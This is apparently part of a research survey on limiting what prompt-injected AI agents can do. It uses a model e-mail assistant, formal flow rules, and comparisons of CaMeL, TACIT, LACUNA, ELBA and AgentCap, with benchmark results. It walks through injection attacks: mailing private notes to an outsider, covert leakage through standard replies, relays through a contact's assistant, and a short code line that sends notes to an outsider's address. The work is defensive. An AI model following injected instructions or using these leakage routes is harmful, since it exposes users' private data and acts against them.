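An e-mail assistant shows how much harm the bound does not rule out when the analysis treats the model as an arbitrary program. The assistant here is an invented example that closely resembles Email-Bot, the imaginary agent in Meta's developer guide *Agents Rule of Two* (2025). Email-Bot reads mail from anybody, searches the user's inbox and sends replies for her.

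The model reads the user's inbox, calendar and private notes. It can write to the calendar, send mail to any address and show text on her screen. An outsider can write to the inbox. The harness carries out the model's calls and adds no checks.

The bound depends on some details of the tools. The calendar tool cannot invite guests, only the user sees the calendar, and the mail server rejects forged sender addresses. The screen shows plain text without images or links. Willison (2025) points out in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that loading an image or offering the user a link to click can leak data, because the requested address can contain the stolen text.

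### Three rules and seven goals

Three rules describe what can happen. P stands for a person, M for a language model, and R and S for places that hold text:

```
1.  writes(P, R)   reads(M, R)    =>  steers(P, M)
2.  steers(P, M)   writes(M, S)   =>  writes(P, S)
3.  reads(M, R)    writes(M, S)   =>  flows(R, S)
```

Under rule 1, anyone who writes something the model reads may steer it. Under rule 2, anyone who steers the model has authority over its tools, so `writes(P, S)` covers both what P can write directly and what P can get a model to write. Under rule 3, anything the model reads may flow to anywhere it writes.

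None of the rules contains "not", so the calculation works as it does in SCOLL, which Spiessens and colleagues describe as a subset of the database query language Datalog. *Capability Safety as Datalog* (2026) proves that working out what a group of agents can reach with their combined capabilities is equivalent to evaluating a simple form of Datalog.

In SCOLL's notation, the goals are:

```
Safety
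  !flows(notes, mail_stranger)       outsider does not learn the notes
  !writes(outsider, mail_contact)    outsider does not cause mail to
  !writes(outsider, mail_other)        third parties
  !writes(outsider, calendar)        outsider does not change the calendar

Liveness
  flows(inbox, screen)               summarise the inbox
  flows(inbox, mail_contact)         answer a contact
  flows(inbox, mail_stranger)        answer a new correspondent
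  flows(inbox, calendar)             add an event that arrived by mail
```

The place `mail_stranger` stands for mail to strangers who have written to the user, and `mail_other` stands for mail to anyone else outside her address book. The outsider and the honest new correspondent share `mail_stranger` because the harness cannot distinguish them. As before, meeting a liveness goal shows only that the design does not rule the job out.

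### Version A, line by line

```
Given
 1     writes(outsider, inbox)
 2     reads(model, inbox)
 3     reads(model, notes)
 4     reads(model, calendar)
 5     writes(model, calendar)
 6     writes(model, mail_stranger)
 7     writes(model, mail_contact)
 8     writes(model, mail_other)
 9     writes(model, screen)

Round 1
10     steers(outsider, model)           rule 1, from 1 and 2
11     flows(inbox, calendar)            rule 3, from 2 and 5
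12     flows(inbox, mail_stranger)       rule 3, from 2 and 6
13     flows(inbox, mail_contact)        rule 3, from 2 and 7
14     flows(inbox, mail_other)          rule 3, from 2 and 8
15     flows(inbox, screen)              rule 3, from 2 and 9
16     flows(notes, calendar)            rule 3, from 3 and 5
17     flows(notes, mail_stranger)       rule 3, from 3 and 6
18     flows(notes, mail_contact)        rule 3, from 3 and 7
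19     flows(notes, mail_other)          rule 3, from 3 and 8
20     flows(notes, screen)              rule 3, from 3 and 9
21-25  flows(calendar, S) for the        rule 3, from 4 and 5-9
       same five places

Round 2
26     writes(outsider, calendar)        rule 2, from 10 and 5
27     writes(outsider, mail_stranger)   rule 2, from 10 and 6
28     writes(outsider, mail_contact)    rule 2, from 10 and 7
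29     writes(outsider, mail_other)      rule 2, from 10 and 8
30     writes(outsider, screen)          rule 2, from 10 and 9

Round 3
       nothing new
```

The fixpoint has 30 facts. All four jobs are possible (lines 11, 12, 13 and 15), but every safety goal fails. The outsider may learn the notes (line 17), cause mail to be sent to third parties (lines 28 and 29) and change the calendar (line 26).

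In round 3, lines 26 and 4 together give line 10 again. This adds no new fact, but it shows that the calendar is a second way for the outsider to steer the model. If the outsider gets the model to write an event today, its text can steer the model next month, long after the user has deleted the original message.

Line 30 breaks none of the goals, but it means the outsider can falsify the summary. For example, he could make it report that a supplier has changed its bank account. None of the versions below prevents this, since summarising his mail requires reading it.

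### Four versions

In version B, a proxy in front of the mail service sends mail only to addresses in the user's address book. In version C, one model reads the mail but has no tools, a second model plans from the user's request alone, and trusted code connects the two. Version D is version A plus an open network connection and a shell, which is a tool that runs any command on the user's computer.

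| Goal | A: as given | B: contacts only | C: two models | D: A plus shell |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Outsider does not learn the notes | fails | **holds** | **holds** | fails |
| Outsider does not cause mail to third parties | fails | **fails for contacts only** | **outsider may choose wording only** | fails |
| Outsider does not change the calendar | fails | fails | **outsider may choose details only** | fails |
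| Summarise the inbox | possible | possible | possible | possible |
| Answer a contact | possible | possible | possible | possible |
| Answer a new correspondent | possible | **impossible** | possible | possible |
| Add an event | possible | possible | possible | possible |

Bold cells differ from version A. The column for C assumes that the planning model plans only what the user asked for.

In version B, the proxy removes lines 6 and 8 and everything that follows from them, which leaves 20 facts. The notes can no longer flow to a stranger, so the first safety goal holds. The assistant also can't answer a new correspondent, because that job and the theft of the notes both depended on line 6.

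Line 7 remains, so the outsider can still make the assistant write to the user's contacts. Meta suggests limiting mail to trusted recipients as one remedy for Email-Bot, and this does stop the outsider from mailing the notes to himself. But Meta also lists phishing messages to the user's friends among the harms of a hijacked Email-Bot, and her friends are in her address book. The calendar goal still fails because the proxy handles only mail.

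The first cell in this column depends on two further conditions. Only the user may edit the address book. If the harness added everyone she had ever answered, the outsider would need only one reply from her to get onto the list. Her contacts must also not pass her mail on. Suppose that Carol, a contact, has an assistant like version A. The outsider can then get the notes in two steps:

1. He steers the user's assistant into sending Carol the notes, with instructions for her assistant.
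2. Carol's assistant reads the message, follows the instructions and mails the notes to the outsider.

Adding Carol's assistant to the model as a second language model would reveal this path.

**Version C.** Suppose the user asks the assistant to put the meeting from a new supplier's mail in her calendar. The planner, which has read only this request, writes a short plan:

```
m = latest mail from the new supplier
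t = reader(m, "Give the title, date and time of the meeting")
add_event(t)
```

The code fetches the message, passes it to the reader, and puts the reader's answer in the calendar. The three rules then give:

```
Given     writes(outsider, inbox)    reads(reader, inbox)
          writes(reader, answers)
          writes(user, request)      reads(planner, request)
          writes(planner, plan)

Round 1   steers(outsider, reader)   flows(inbox, answers)
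          steers(user, planner)      flows(request, plan)

Round 2   writes(outsider, answers)  writes(user, plan)

Round 3   nothing new
```

The fact `writes(outsider, plan)` never appears, so the outsider no longer chooses the action. He may still choose the values in it, because the code copies the reader's answers into whatever the plan calls for.

This explains the three changed cells. The outsider does not learn the notes, because the reader never sees them and only a plan can fetch them. He cannot start a message to a contact, but he may influence the wording of one the user requested. He cannot add or delete an event on his own, but when the user asks to add the meeting in the outsider's e-mail, the outsider sets its title, date and time.

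An outsider can also do harm through values. If the user asks for a reply to his enquiry, the reader drafts it after reading his text, and he may get the reader to accept his price in the user's name. Willison quotes a paper on agent design patterns that would make it "impossible for that input to trigger any consequential actions". Version C, like the published systems built on this plan, stops the input from triggering an action, but the input still affects the consequences of actions that the user triggers.

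The separation is also easy to lose. Suppose a developer lets the planner read the calendar so it can understand requests such as "move my next meeting". The outsider can already influence event titles, so rule 1 gives `steers(outsider, planner)`, and rule 2 gives `writes(outsider, plan)`. The outsider can then choose actions again.

The column for C is based on the assumption that the planner, which is also a language model, is harmless unless somebody steers it. An analyst who treats the planner as an arbitrary program must allow for a plan that mails the notes to a stranger, or one that uses the reader's output to choose the recipient and the text of a message. Every safety goal then fails again. If the code blocks text from the notes from entering any message, the first goal holds again without relying on the planner, but the user can no longer ask the assistant to send somebody an extract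 from the notes.

**Version D** has the same results in the table as version A, because A already failed every safety goal. But the fixpoint grows from 30 facts to 56. The shell lets the model read and write both the web and the files on the computer, so it can write to seven places instead of five and read from five instead of three. The outsider may now alter the user's files, and the files' contents may flow to the web. A fourth safety goal that protected the files would hold in A and fail in D.

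Adding the shell to version B does more visible damage. The model can then post the notes on a website that the outsider reads, or connect to another mail service and write to anybody. The proxy still works as designed, but the model can bypass it.

### What makes the bound loose?

Each unwanted fact in a fixpoint has a derivation, which the analyst can trace to find the cause. Spiessens expects this to be relatively easy in a model of this kind. The analyst can then ask whether a hostile program in the language model's place could bring the fact about, given the actual software. If it couldn't, her description of the tools is too coarse, and refining it will remove the fact. If it could, the bound is correct for a hostile language model, and a better description of the tools won't change it.

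In version C, the outsider's influence over the wording of messages to contacts comes from a coarse description. The fact `reads(reader, inbox)` treats the inbox as one place, so his text appears to affect every answer the reader gives, including a draft reply to Carol. But suppose the code starts a fresh session of the reader for each message. The analyst can then split the inbox into strangers' mail and contacts' mail, and split the reader in the same way:

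```
writes(outsider, strangers_mail)
reads(reader_1, strangers_mail)     writes(reader_1, answers_1)
reads(reader_2, contacts_mail)      writes(reader_2, answers_2)
```

The outsider steers only `reader_1`. Replies to contacts use `answers_2`, so he can no longer affect their wording unless a contact's message quotes him or the user asks the assistant to pass on what he wrote. The software is the same as before. The split doesn't help with the calendar, because the event he proposed comes from his message.

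If the calendar tool's code can add events but cannot change or delete them, `writes(outsider, calendar)` overstates the harm in versions A and B. The outsider can fill the calendar with false meetings, but he can't change or remove real ones.

*Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (2026) takes this kind of refinement further by giving each tool its own rule for how sensitive data moves through it. In its example, an agent runs a redaction tool on one file, merges the result with another, copies the merged text to a third file and mails that file to an outside address. The rules trace the third file back to its sources, so the analysis need not assume that the file contains everything the agent has handled. The paper applies the rules to a record of an agent's actions and accounts for the chance that redaction fails, using the tool's past failure rate. An analyst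 could write similar rules before an agent runs, but a sound worst-case version would have to assume that redaction may fail unless she can rely on the tool.

Such rules help only when text moves from file to file without passing through the model. Once the model has read a note, it can retype, paraphrase or encode the note in any message it writes. Rule 3 is therefore exact for a hostile model.

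That is why no refinement removes line 17, the flow of the notes to a stranger in version A. The line follows from the fact that the software lets the model both read the notes and write to strangers. To remove it, a developer has to remove or narrow one of the two references.

Version B removes the reference for writing to strangers, so the assistant can no longer do a job the user wanted done. The developer could instead narrow the reference. Suppose the proxy also lets the model send a new correspondent one of eight standard replies, such as "Thank you, I will answer by Friday", without adding any text. Each choice could carry three bits of the notes, so 100 replies could carry 300 bits, or about 37 characters, which is enough for a password. If the proxy sends strangers no more than five replies a day in total, at most 15 bits a day can leak this way. The goal "the outsider does not learn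 the notes" still strictly fails, but the user may accept a leak of that size.

A developer can also divide the references between sessions. For each job, the harness starts a fresh session that holds only the references the job needs:

| Session | Reads | Writes |
|---|---|---|
| Answer a stranger | that stranger's message | mail to that stranger |
| Work with the notes | notes | screen |

The assistant as a whole still reads the notes and writes to strangers, but no session does both, so line 17 disappears and the assistant can answer new correspondents. The user's own choice, such as a button she presses, must determine which session the harness starts, because a model that had read the mail could choose wrongly.

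Shared storage can undo this separation. If the session that works with the notes may write to the calendar and the session that answers strangers may read it, information from the notes can reach a stranger through the calendar. To prevent this, the developer has to remove either the write access or the read access. But without read access, the session that answers strangers cannot reply to "Are you free on Tuesday?"

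The bound for the assistant can therefore be tight for a hostile program and still very loose for the model the user runs. Better tool descriptions only reduce the gap between the calculation and what a hostile program could do. In version A, that gap is already almost zero for the notes, and the goal still fails.

### The lethal trifecta as a special case

Willison, who coined the term "prompt injection", calls a dangerous combination of three features the lethal trifecta. An agent with access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate externally is open to an attacker who wants to steal the data. The same three rules describe this:

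```
writes(P, R)      reads(M, R)       untrusted content
reads(M, private)                   private data
writes(M, S)      reads(P, S)       external communication
    =>  steers(P, M)    flows(private, S)
```

In version A, the outsider (P) steers the model through the inbox (R). The private data, which are the notes, may flow to the outsider's own mail (S), which the outsider can read.

A single product can have all three features. Willison describes an attack on GitHub's connector for agents, which could read public issues filed by anyone, read private repositories, and create pull requests (proposed code changes) that others could read. He notes that companies usually fixed such leaks by blocking the route by which data could leave, and has since argued that the only reliable prevention is to remove one of the three features. Version B does this, but a shell with open network access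 restores a way to send data out.

*No Attack Required* (2026), a study of add-on skills for agents, frames a similar test as a search for a chain of events. The chain must start with sensitive data and end in an action that changes something and can be influenced by input. It is a violation only if it includes no request for user confirmation. The same form of test covers other harms, such as outside input reaching passwords or other credentials.

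The trifecta is narrower than the three rules in one respect. Line 17 depends on the model reading the notes and writing to strangers, but not on the outsider writing to the inbox. If the harness shows the model only mail from contacts the user trusts, one part of the trifecta is gone, but line 17 remains, because the model might still mail the notes to a stranger through a hidden flaw or by mistake. Removing untrusted content works only if the model never leaks data unless somebody tells it to. Version C makes the same assumption about its planner.

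The trifecta also covers only the theft of data. The outsider's power over the calendar follows from lines 1, 2 and 5, and would survive if the developer took the notes away. Willison (2025), in *New prompt injection papers*, acknowledged this limit and welcomed Meta's rule, which adds changes of state to external communication. Under that rule, an agent may have at most two of these properties within a session unless a human or another reliable check supervises it:

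- it processes untrustworthy inputs;
- it has access to sensitive systems or private data;
- it changes state or communicates externally.

Meta's original diagram labelled any two of the three properties "safe". Willison objected that untrustworthy inputs and the power to change state can do harm without any private data, as with the calendar here. Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that any system that matters to the user counts as sensitive, and Meta changed the label to "lower risk". On that reading, the calendar is a sensitive system, so version B still has all three properties. Meta's rule would therefore require supervision even though the proxy keeps the notes from the outsider.

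## What does checking the code an agent writes add, and cost?

Version C of the e-mail assistant was only as safe as its planner, because the trusted code ran whatever plan the planner wrote. But a plan is a program, so ordinary software can examine it. If that software stops every plan that would break a rule, the rule holds no matter how hostile the planner is. This claim has the same form as the theorems about arbitrary code, except that the unknown program must also pass a check.

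In version A, a hostile model could read the user's notes, disguise them and mail them to an outsider. A planner that has read only the user's request has to write something like this instead:

```
n = read_notes()
send_mail("outsider@example.com", n)
```

The variable `n` connects the two lines. The planner never receives the contents of `n`, so it can't retype them. Disguising them would take another step in the program, which the checking software can follow. The analysis therefore no longer includes the fact `reads(model, notes)`, although the assistant can still work with the notes.

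### Labels that follow the data

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues presented in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), tracks data while the plan runs. It starts from the same division as version C, which Willison had proposed in 2023, and calls the model that reads documents the quarantined model. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), the planner writes a program in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter runs the program, makes the tool calls and labels each value the quarantined model extracts. Before each tool call, the interpreter evaluates a policy, a Python function that allows or refuses the call. The literature on CaMeL calls the labels capabilities, but they describe data, whereas this report uses "capability" to mean a reference.

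Suppose the policy for mail is that only the user's accountant may receive text derived from the notes. A hostile planner might try a translation:

```
n = read_notes()                         label: notes
t = reader(n, "Translate into French")   label: notes
send_mail("outsider@example.com", t)     policy refuses
```

A filter that searched outgoing mail for sentences from the notes would miss the French translation. The translation keeps the notes' label because a result inherits the labels of all its inputs.

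The goal about mail to third parties is harder to meet. A hostile planner can write a contact's address and an abusive message into the plan. Neither comes from a document, so no label marks them as suspect. If the policy accepts text that the planner wrote, this goal still depends on the planner, as it did in version C.

The interpreter is part of the trusted base, which is everything that must work correctly for the bound to hold. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which defines a small formal language for agents and proves a theorem about its information flow, identifies two weaknesses in CaMeL's interpreter. First, labels spread through it in some unexpected ways. Second, when a plan fails, CaMeL lets the planner try again in a loop that runs outside the part of the interpreter that checks policies. Each new attempt starts without labels, even though it depends on error messages from the previous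 one. If a plan expects a date and the quarantined model returns a sentence from the outsider's mail, the error message could carry that sentence to the planner. CaMeL censors the messages to limit this, but without a formal guarantee.

The planner also has to write code to handle a tool's output before seeing any of that output. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which extends CaMeL to several cooperating agents, reports that CaMeL performed reasonably only after the tool descriptions fully specified what each tool returns. The paper describes writing these specifications as a modest, one-time task for each set of tools.

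### Checking before anything runs

CaMeL's interpreter detects a forbidden call only when the plan reaches it. TACIT, the system Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) present in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, rejects a program containing such a call before any of it runs. TACIT makes an agent write its actions in the programming language Scala 3. The researchers treat the cloud-hosted model as a possible attacker and don't trust its code or any text from tools and web pages. They trust the Scala compiler, a library of about 1,000 lines, the software that runs the compiled code and, optionally, a second model on the user's own machine.

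The compiler uses an experimental feature called capture checking. In Scala, a capability is an ordinary value, such as a handle `f` that permits writing to one file. Capture checking works out which capabilities each function could use and records them in the function's type:

```
s => s.toUpperCase      type: String -> String
s => f.write(s)         type: String ->{f} Unit
```

The braces contain the function's capture set. The upper function captures nothing, so it is pure, meaning it can only compute a result from its input. A capture set includes every capability the function could use, though it may also list some that the function never uses. It is therefore a sound bound in the sense used throughout this literature, and it is calculated for every function in the program.

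TACIT puts secret data in a wrapper called `Classified`. A program can work on the contents only by giving the wrapper's `map` method a pure function:

```
notes.map(s => s.toUpperCase)     accepted
notes.map(s => f.write(s))        rejected
```

The compiler rejects the second line without knowing what the notes say or why the model wanted to write them to a file. The argument that no accepted program can leak the notes has four steps:

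1. Reading a protected file returns its contents already in the wrapper, and printing the wrapper shows only asterisks. A method that reveals the contents requires a permission that the agent lacks.
2. `map` accepts only pure functions, so the code that handles the contents can't write a file, contact a server or call a tool.
3. The result of `map` is in a wrapper too.
4. The compiler's safe mode forbids the language features, such as unchecked type conversions, that would let a program hide a capability from the check.

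The cloud model can therefore request a summary of the notes without reading them. The library passes the wrapped notes to the local model, which returns a wrapped summary. The user's screen shows the text, while the cloud model receives asterisks in its place. The guarantee depends on the local model not leaking what it reads, but it holds even if the model's answers are wrong. If a note contains a planted instruction, the local model may write a false summary, but that summary stays wrapped.

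TACIT's guarantee doesn't cover side channels, such as code that takes longer when a secret begins with a certain letter. It also doesn't cover outside programs that the agent starts, so the list of permitted programs has to be short. The core type system has machine-checked proofs, but Odersky and colleagues say a further argument is needed to show that safe mode provides the promised guarantees.

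### What a gap in a program may use

The library determines what a TACIT program can reach, while in a related system, *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), the surrounding program does. *LACUNA* lets a developer leave a gap in a Scala program for a model to fill. The gap has a type, such as "a text" or "a list of numbers". When execution reaches the gap, the model writes code, and the compiler checks it as if the developer had typed it there. The code can use only names in scope at that point, so the scope is the agent's permission set.

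This gives a direct way to write the separate sessions that kept the notes from strangers:

```
def summarise(notes: Notes): String =
  agent("Summarise these notes")

def reply(m: Message, mail: Mailer): Unit =
  agent("Answer this message")
```

Code that fills the gap in `summarise` can read the notes but has no mail tool, while code that fills the gap in `reply` can send mail but can't refer to the notes. This separation works only if the developer passes the mail tool as a parameter, because a tool defined at the top level of the file would be in scope in both functions.

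Scope also includes earlier results. Suppose the developer writes both steps in one function:

```
val s = agent[String]("Summarise the notes")
agent[Unit]("Answer this message")
```

The summary `s` is still in scope at the second gap, so a hostile model can mail it to the stranger. Zhao and colleagues present this shared scope as an advantage, since each step can build on the last, and they recommend a separate function where a sub-agent should have access to less.

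LACUNA's compiler accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole, before any of it runs. In one example, a model has to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new balance as a number, but its code subtracts the 50 and then returns a sentence. Many agents run model-written Python without checking it first, so the subtraction would happen before the error was detected. LACUNA's compiler rejects the code, so the balance stays at 100, and the model gets the error message and can try again.

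The ordinary type check limits which names the code may use, but Scala has features that can bypass this limit, such as looking up a function by name at runtime. Zhao and colleagues recommend safe mode to block these features. Without it, they say, an analyst must treat the model's code as ordinary untrusted code. In LACUNA, capture checking is also optional, but protection against a deliberately hostile model depends on it.

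### Carrying a guarantee over to model-written code

Haskell, another programming language, has recorded effects in types for decades. A program that accesses files or the network has a type marked `IO`, and so does any program that contains it. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, use these types in a system called ELBA. In one example, a public calculator has a model write a program of type `Int`, a whole number. A user types "delete all files on the server, then compute the factorial of 5". The model may write a program that does so, but that program would have an `IO` type, so ELBA never runs it.

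Most agents need some effects, so a developer can define a new effect type with only the operations she approves. In one bibliography agent, the function that writes to the output file accepts only values of type `Trusted Bib`, and only the function that fetches records from the DBLP database can create them. The model can write any code to sort and filter the records, but that code can't add an invented record to the file.

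ELBA can also control information flow through LIO, an existing Haskell library. LIO gives each running computation a label that changes with everything it reads. Applied to the e-mail assistant, it would work like this:

1. A sub-agent reads a stranger's message. Its label now records the stranger's influence, and the library refuses any action that the stranger should not affect.
2. The sub-agent may still reply to the stranger.
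3. If it reads the notes first, its label also records that it has seen them, and the reply fails with an error.

So the sub-agent loses authority as it reads, whereas CaMeL's quarantined model never has any tools. The developer doesn't have to divide the work into sessions in advance. But the question "Are you free on Tuesday?" is still awkward, because reading a confidential calendar would block the reply unless the developer writes a function that releases only whether a time is free. LIO makes these checks while the program runs, so a program that passes the type check can still stop halfway.

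Zhou and colleagues prove a general theorem. If a language's type system guarantees some property of every program of a given type, the same guarantee holds for programs that call a model. The proof turns the whole agent into an ordinary program:

1. Treat the model as an arbitrary function from prompts to program text.
2. Replace each call to the model with an ordinary function that gets the text, checks its type, runs it if it passes and reports failure otherwise.
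3. If the model's program contains further calls to the model, replace those too. A limit on how deeply calls may nest ensures that this ends.
4. The result is an ordinary program of the same type with the same visible behaviour, so the original guarantee applies to it.

The theorem assumes nothing about what the model writes except that the same prompt always gets the same answer. Zhou and colleagues consider this assumption harmless for the properties they study. The theorem guarantees only what the developer's type requires, so it doesn't rule out a harmful action that the type permits.

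### How the designs fared against attacks

Most of the published tests use AgentDojo, a benchmark that Debenedetti and others released in 2024. It gives an agent user tasks in a simulated bank, office, Slack workspace or travel service and automatically checks whether they were completed. The attacks are in the tools' output, such as a Slack message that asks the agent to do something else. Testers pair every user task with every attacker's goal, so the Slack suite's 21 user tasks and 5 goals produce 105 pairs.

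Odersky and colleagues converted all four suites to TACIT, and Zhao and colleagues later converted them to LACUNA. Both compared their results with scores copied from the CaMeL paper. The percentages show how many user tasks the agent completed while under attack, and the last column adds up the attacks that succeeded in 949 trials:

| Model and system | Banking | Office | Slack | Travel | Attacks |
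|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, CaMeL | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% | 0 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% | 0 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, LACUNA | 63.2% | 56.3% | 42.9% | 63.6% | 7 |
| o4-mini, CaMeL | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% | 1 |
| o4-mini, TACIT | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% | 1 |
| o4-mini, LACUNA | 66.0% | 55.5% | 49.5% | 71.4% | 1 |

TACIT's one failure is a quirk of the scoring. An attacker had planted praise for a rival hotel in some reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, and the benchmark counted the mention of the rival as a successful attack.

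LACUNA's eight failures are more informative. Zhao and colleagues don't describe each one, but they link them to a limit of the design. It doesn't stop an attacker who persuades the model to misuse a capability that its task requires. Such an attack stays inside the bound, like the landlord's e-mail asking for the tax summary.

Odersky and colleagues also built their own test around a software project with a folder of secrets. It pairs 12 legitimate tasks with 10 planted attacks and adds 11 requests in which the user asks for the secrets, sometimes while posing as an administrator. They ran everything with the secrets in wrappers and again with the secrets as plain text:

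| Model | No leak, wrapped | No leak, plain | Tasks done, wrapped | Tasks done, plain |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 131 of 131 | 129 of 131 | 99.2% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 131 of 131 | 120 of 131 | 90.0% | 88.3% |

When the secrets were plain text, MiniMax revealed them in response to 8 of the 11 direct requests. With the wrapper, security didn't depend on which of the two models was used. The wrapper also didn't reduce the number of tasks completed, though Odersky and colleagues suspect that Sonnet's low score without it is partly an artifact, since Sonnet often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user.

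The standard AgentDojo attacks have become too weak to test a design like ELBA. Zhou and colleagues ran Opus 4.7, Opus 4.8, GPT 5.4 and Sonnet 5 on the Slack suite, and no attack succeeded even with all policies switched off. They then changed ELBA's code so that any sub-agent that read a planted instruction received that instruction as its task. This is the worst-case assumption turned into an experiment. Each model went through 735 trials:

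| Model | Attacks stopped, policies on | Attacks stopped, policies off |
|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 735 | 425 |
| Opus 4.8 | 735 | 460 |
| GPT 5.4 | 735 | 621 |
| Sonnet 5 | 735 | 540 |

The benchmark's automatic scoring flagged 29 of the 2,940 runs with policies on. All 29 involved only opening a fixed web address, and the team reviewed each one by hand and found no violation.

None of these experiments used adaptive attackers like those of Nasr and colleagues. For attacks that try to persuade the model, this matters less than it did for the defences those attackers broke, because these designs already assume the model may obey the attacker. An adaptive attacker would do better to look for a mistake in the compiler, a tool whose output lacks a label, or a policy that permits too much. Testers could look for the same flaws by submitting hostile programs directly to the checker. Zhao and colleagues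 ran about 400 test programs through theirs, all with the expected result, but the bad programs imitated common agent mistakes, not deliberate attempts to break out.

Other groups have re-run CaMeL, but in papers that propose extensions or competitors to it. The results for TACIT, LACUNA and ELBA come from their own authors, and the TACIT and LACUNA teams share five members.

### What the checks cost in completed tasks

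Having to write code that passes the check can make a model do worse at its tasks. Odersky and colleagues measured this effect on τ²-bench, which simulates conversations with customers of an airline and a shop. Three models each did slightly better in both settings when they wrote Scala than when they made ordinary tool calls, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points, possibly because the compiler's error messages help a model correct itself. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software faults, MiniMax M2.5's score fell from 43.3% to 41.7%.

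Models did worse on τ²-bench through LACUNA than with ordinary tool calls. DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 90.0% of 392 tasks with ordinary tool calls and 76.0% through LACUNA, a difference of about 55 tasks, though Zhao and colleagues call this "on par". Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite's score fell from 33.2% to 29.1%. Performance through LACUNA depends heavily on how well the model writes Scala. The compiler rejected 22.4% of DeepSeek's code for the shop tasks and 89% of Gemini's code for the telecom tasks.

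Policies can cost much more. Zhou and colleagues ran ELBA and CaMeL on the 21 Slack tasks without any attack:

| Model | ELBA, no policies | ELBA, policies | CaMeL, no policies | CaMeL, policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 18 | 10 | 15 | 5 |
| Opus 4.8 | 16 | 9 | 16 | 6 |
| GPT 5.4 | 16 | 10 | 17 | 5 |
| Sonnet 5 | 14 | 8 | 13 | 4 |
| Total (of 84) | 64 | 37 | 61 | 20 |

Without policies, the two systems perform about equally, and with only 21 tasks the difference for any one model could be chance. With policies, ELBA loses two fifths of the tasks it had completed and CaMeL loses two thirds. Zhou and colleagues attribute ELBA's loss to policies that also rule out legitimate behaviour. For example, a legitimate Slack task may require the agent to act on what a message says, as an attack does.

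ELBA's advantage over CaMeL may come as much from its policies as from its design, since the two systems use different policies. ELBA also took about three times as long, because it calls the model again as it reads new data. Policies had a similar effect in *The LLMbda Calculus*, where turning them on halved CaMeL's task completion on the banking suite, to 37.5%. With policies on for both, the paper's own agent, Randori, completed about twice as many tasks as CaMeL and stopped all but 2 of 1,296 attacks. More precise labels or better-chosen policies can therefore recover some of the tasks lost to a bound of this kind.

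These comparisons don't show the full cost relative to an agent with no defence. CaMeL without policies still has two separate models, and none of the papers introducing TACIT, LACUNA and ELBA compares its system with a conventional tool-calling agent on AgentDojo.

### The four designs compared

| | CaMeL | TACIT | LACUNA | ELBA |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Trusted | Interpreter, labels, policies | Compiler, library, runtime, local model's secrecy | Compiler, runtime, surrounding program | Haskell, effect libraries, surrounding program |
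| Proved | No formal guarantee for the retry loop | Core type system, but not yet safe mode | No new theorem; relies on the compiler's guarantees | Type guarantees extend to programs that call a model |
| Excluded | Tool calls that break a policy | Wrapped data reaching the cloud model or an unauthorised destination | Effects and data outside the gap's scope | Effects outside the type; flows that labels forbid |
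| Task success | Policies cut 61 of 84 tasks to 20 | -1.7 to +3.7 points against tool calls | -4.1 and -14.0 points against tool calls | Policies cut 64 of 84 tasks to 37 |
| Policy written by | Whoever writes the Python functions for each tool | Whoever writes the tool interface and marks data as secret | The developer, through what is in scope | The developer, through types and labels |

The task-success figures for CaMeL and ELBA measure how much policies reduce success, while those for TACIT and LACUNA measure how much writing checked code reduces it.

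In every column, a person has to decide what the checker should forbid, and the checker can't detect a poor decision. In TACIT's version of the AgentDojo travel suite, for example, the tool interface wraps hotel reviews, so an instruction planted in a review never reaches the cloud model. But another function returns the user's passport, bank account and credit card numbers as plain text, and the mail function accepts any plain text for any recipient. Those two signatures would let a hostile model mail the card number to a stranger. The interface suits a test in which attackers plant text and the model itself is honest. To treat the model as an attacker, as Odersky and colleagues do in their main design, somebody would also have to wrap the user's details and write a function that lets the agent pay for a hotel without reading the card number.

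## What does checking each tool call add, and cost?

TACIT and LACUNA check a program before it runs. In another family of designs, the model makes ordinary tool calls, and a gateway outside the model controls whether each call takes effect. The gateway may be a proxy in front of the tools, a broker that carries out the calls itself, or a sandbox (limits the operating system enforces on a running program). If the model has no other way to reach the tools, its authority is bounded by whatever the gateway could ever let through.

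Suppose a developer asks a coding agent to add a timeout option to a program, and the gateway follows three rules:

1. The agent may read and change any file in the project folder.
2. It may run the project's tests.
3. It may exchange data with one website that hosts software packages.

The analyst treats the model as an arbitrary program and asks which sequences of calls these rules allow. The model can't read the developer's mail, but it can delete the whole project or copy the source code to the website without breaking any rule. Rule 2 also lets it run any program, because it can rewrite the tests it is allowed to run. The bound therefore includes everything such a program could reach on the developer's computer. To keep the bound small, the gateway has to confine the programs it starts as well as check the calls it receives.

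### Authorising one call at a time

Suresh and Gao (2026), in *AGENTCAP*, make the decision depend on more than the tool's name. They assume that an attacker controls documents, tool outputs or messages between agents, and can use them to choose the model's calls. They trust the gateway, its signing keys and the policy, which a person writes. The model states a purpose with each call it proposes, and a policy engine checks seven conditions:

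- The policy lists the tool.
- The policy lists the stated purpose for that tool.
- No sensitive argument comes only from untrusted text.
- The agent already holds authority for any step that must come first.
- The new authority would not complete a forbidden combination.
- The agent is not suspended.
- Its trust score, which falls after each refusal, is high enough.

If all seven hold, the engine issues a signed token for that action, and a second component verifies the token before forwarding the call. In the banking policy, a token for sending money lasts 30 seconds, covers one payment, and requires the agent to have already obtained authority to look up the balance.

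The condition on arguments adds the check that Mellafe Zuvic found missing from common agent software. AgentCap accepts an account number contained in the user's own request, but refuses to pay into an account whose number appears only in a stranger's document. The printed policy applies this check only to the recipient, so the bound still includes paying the right person the wrong amount. The stated purpose offers little protection against a hostile model, since the model writes it.

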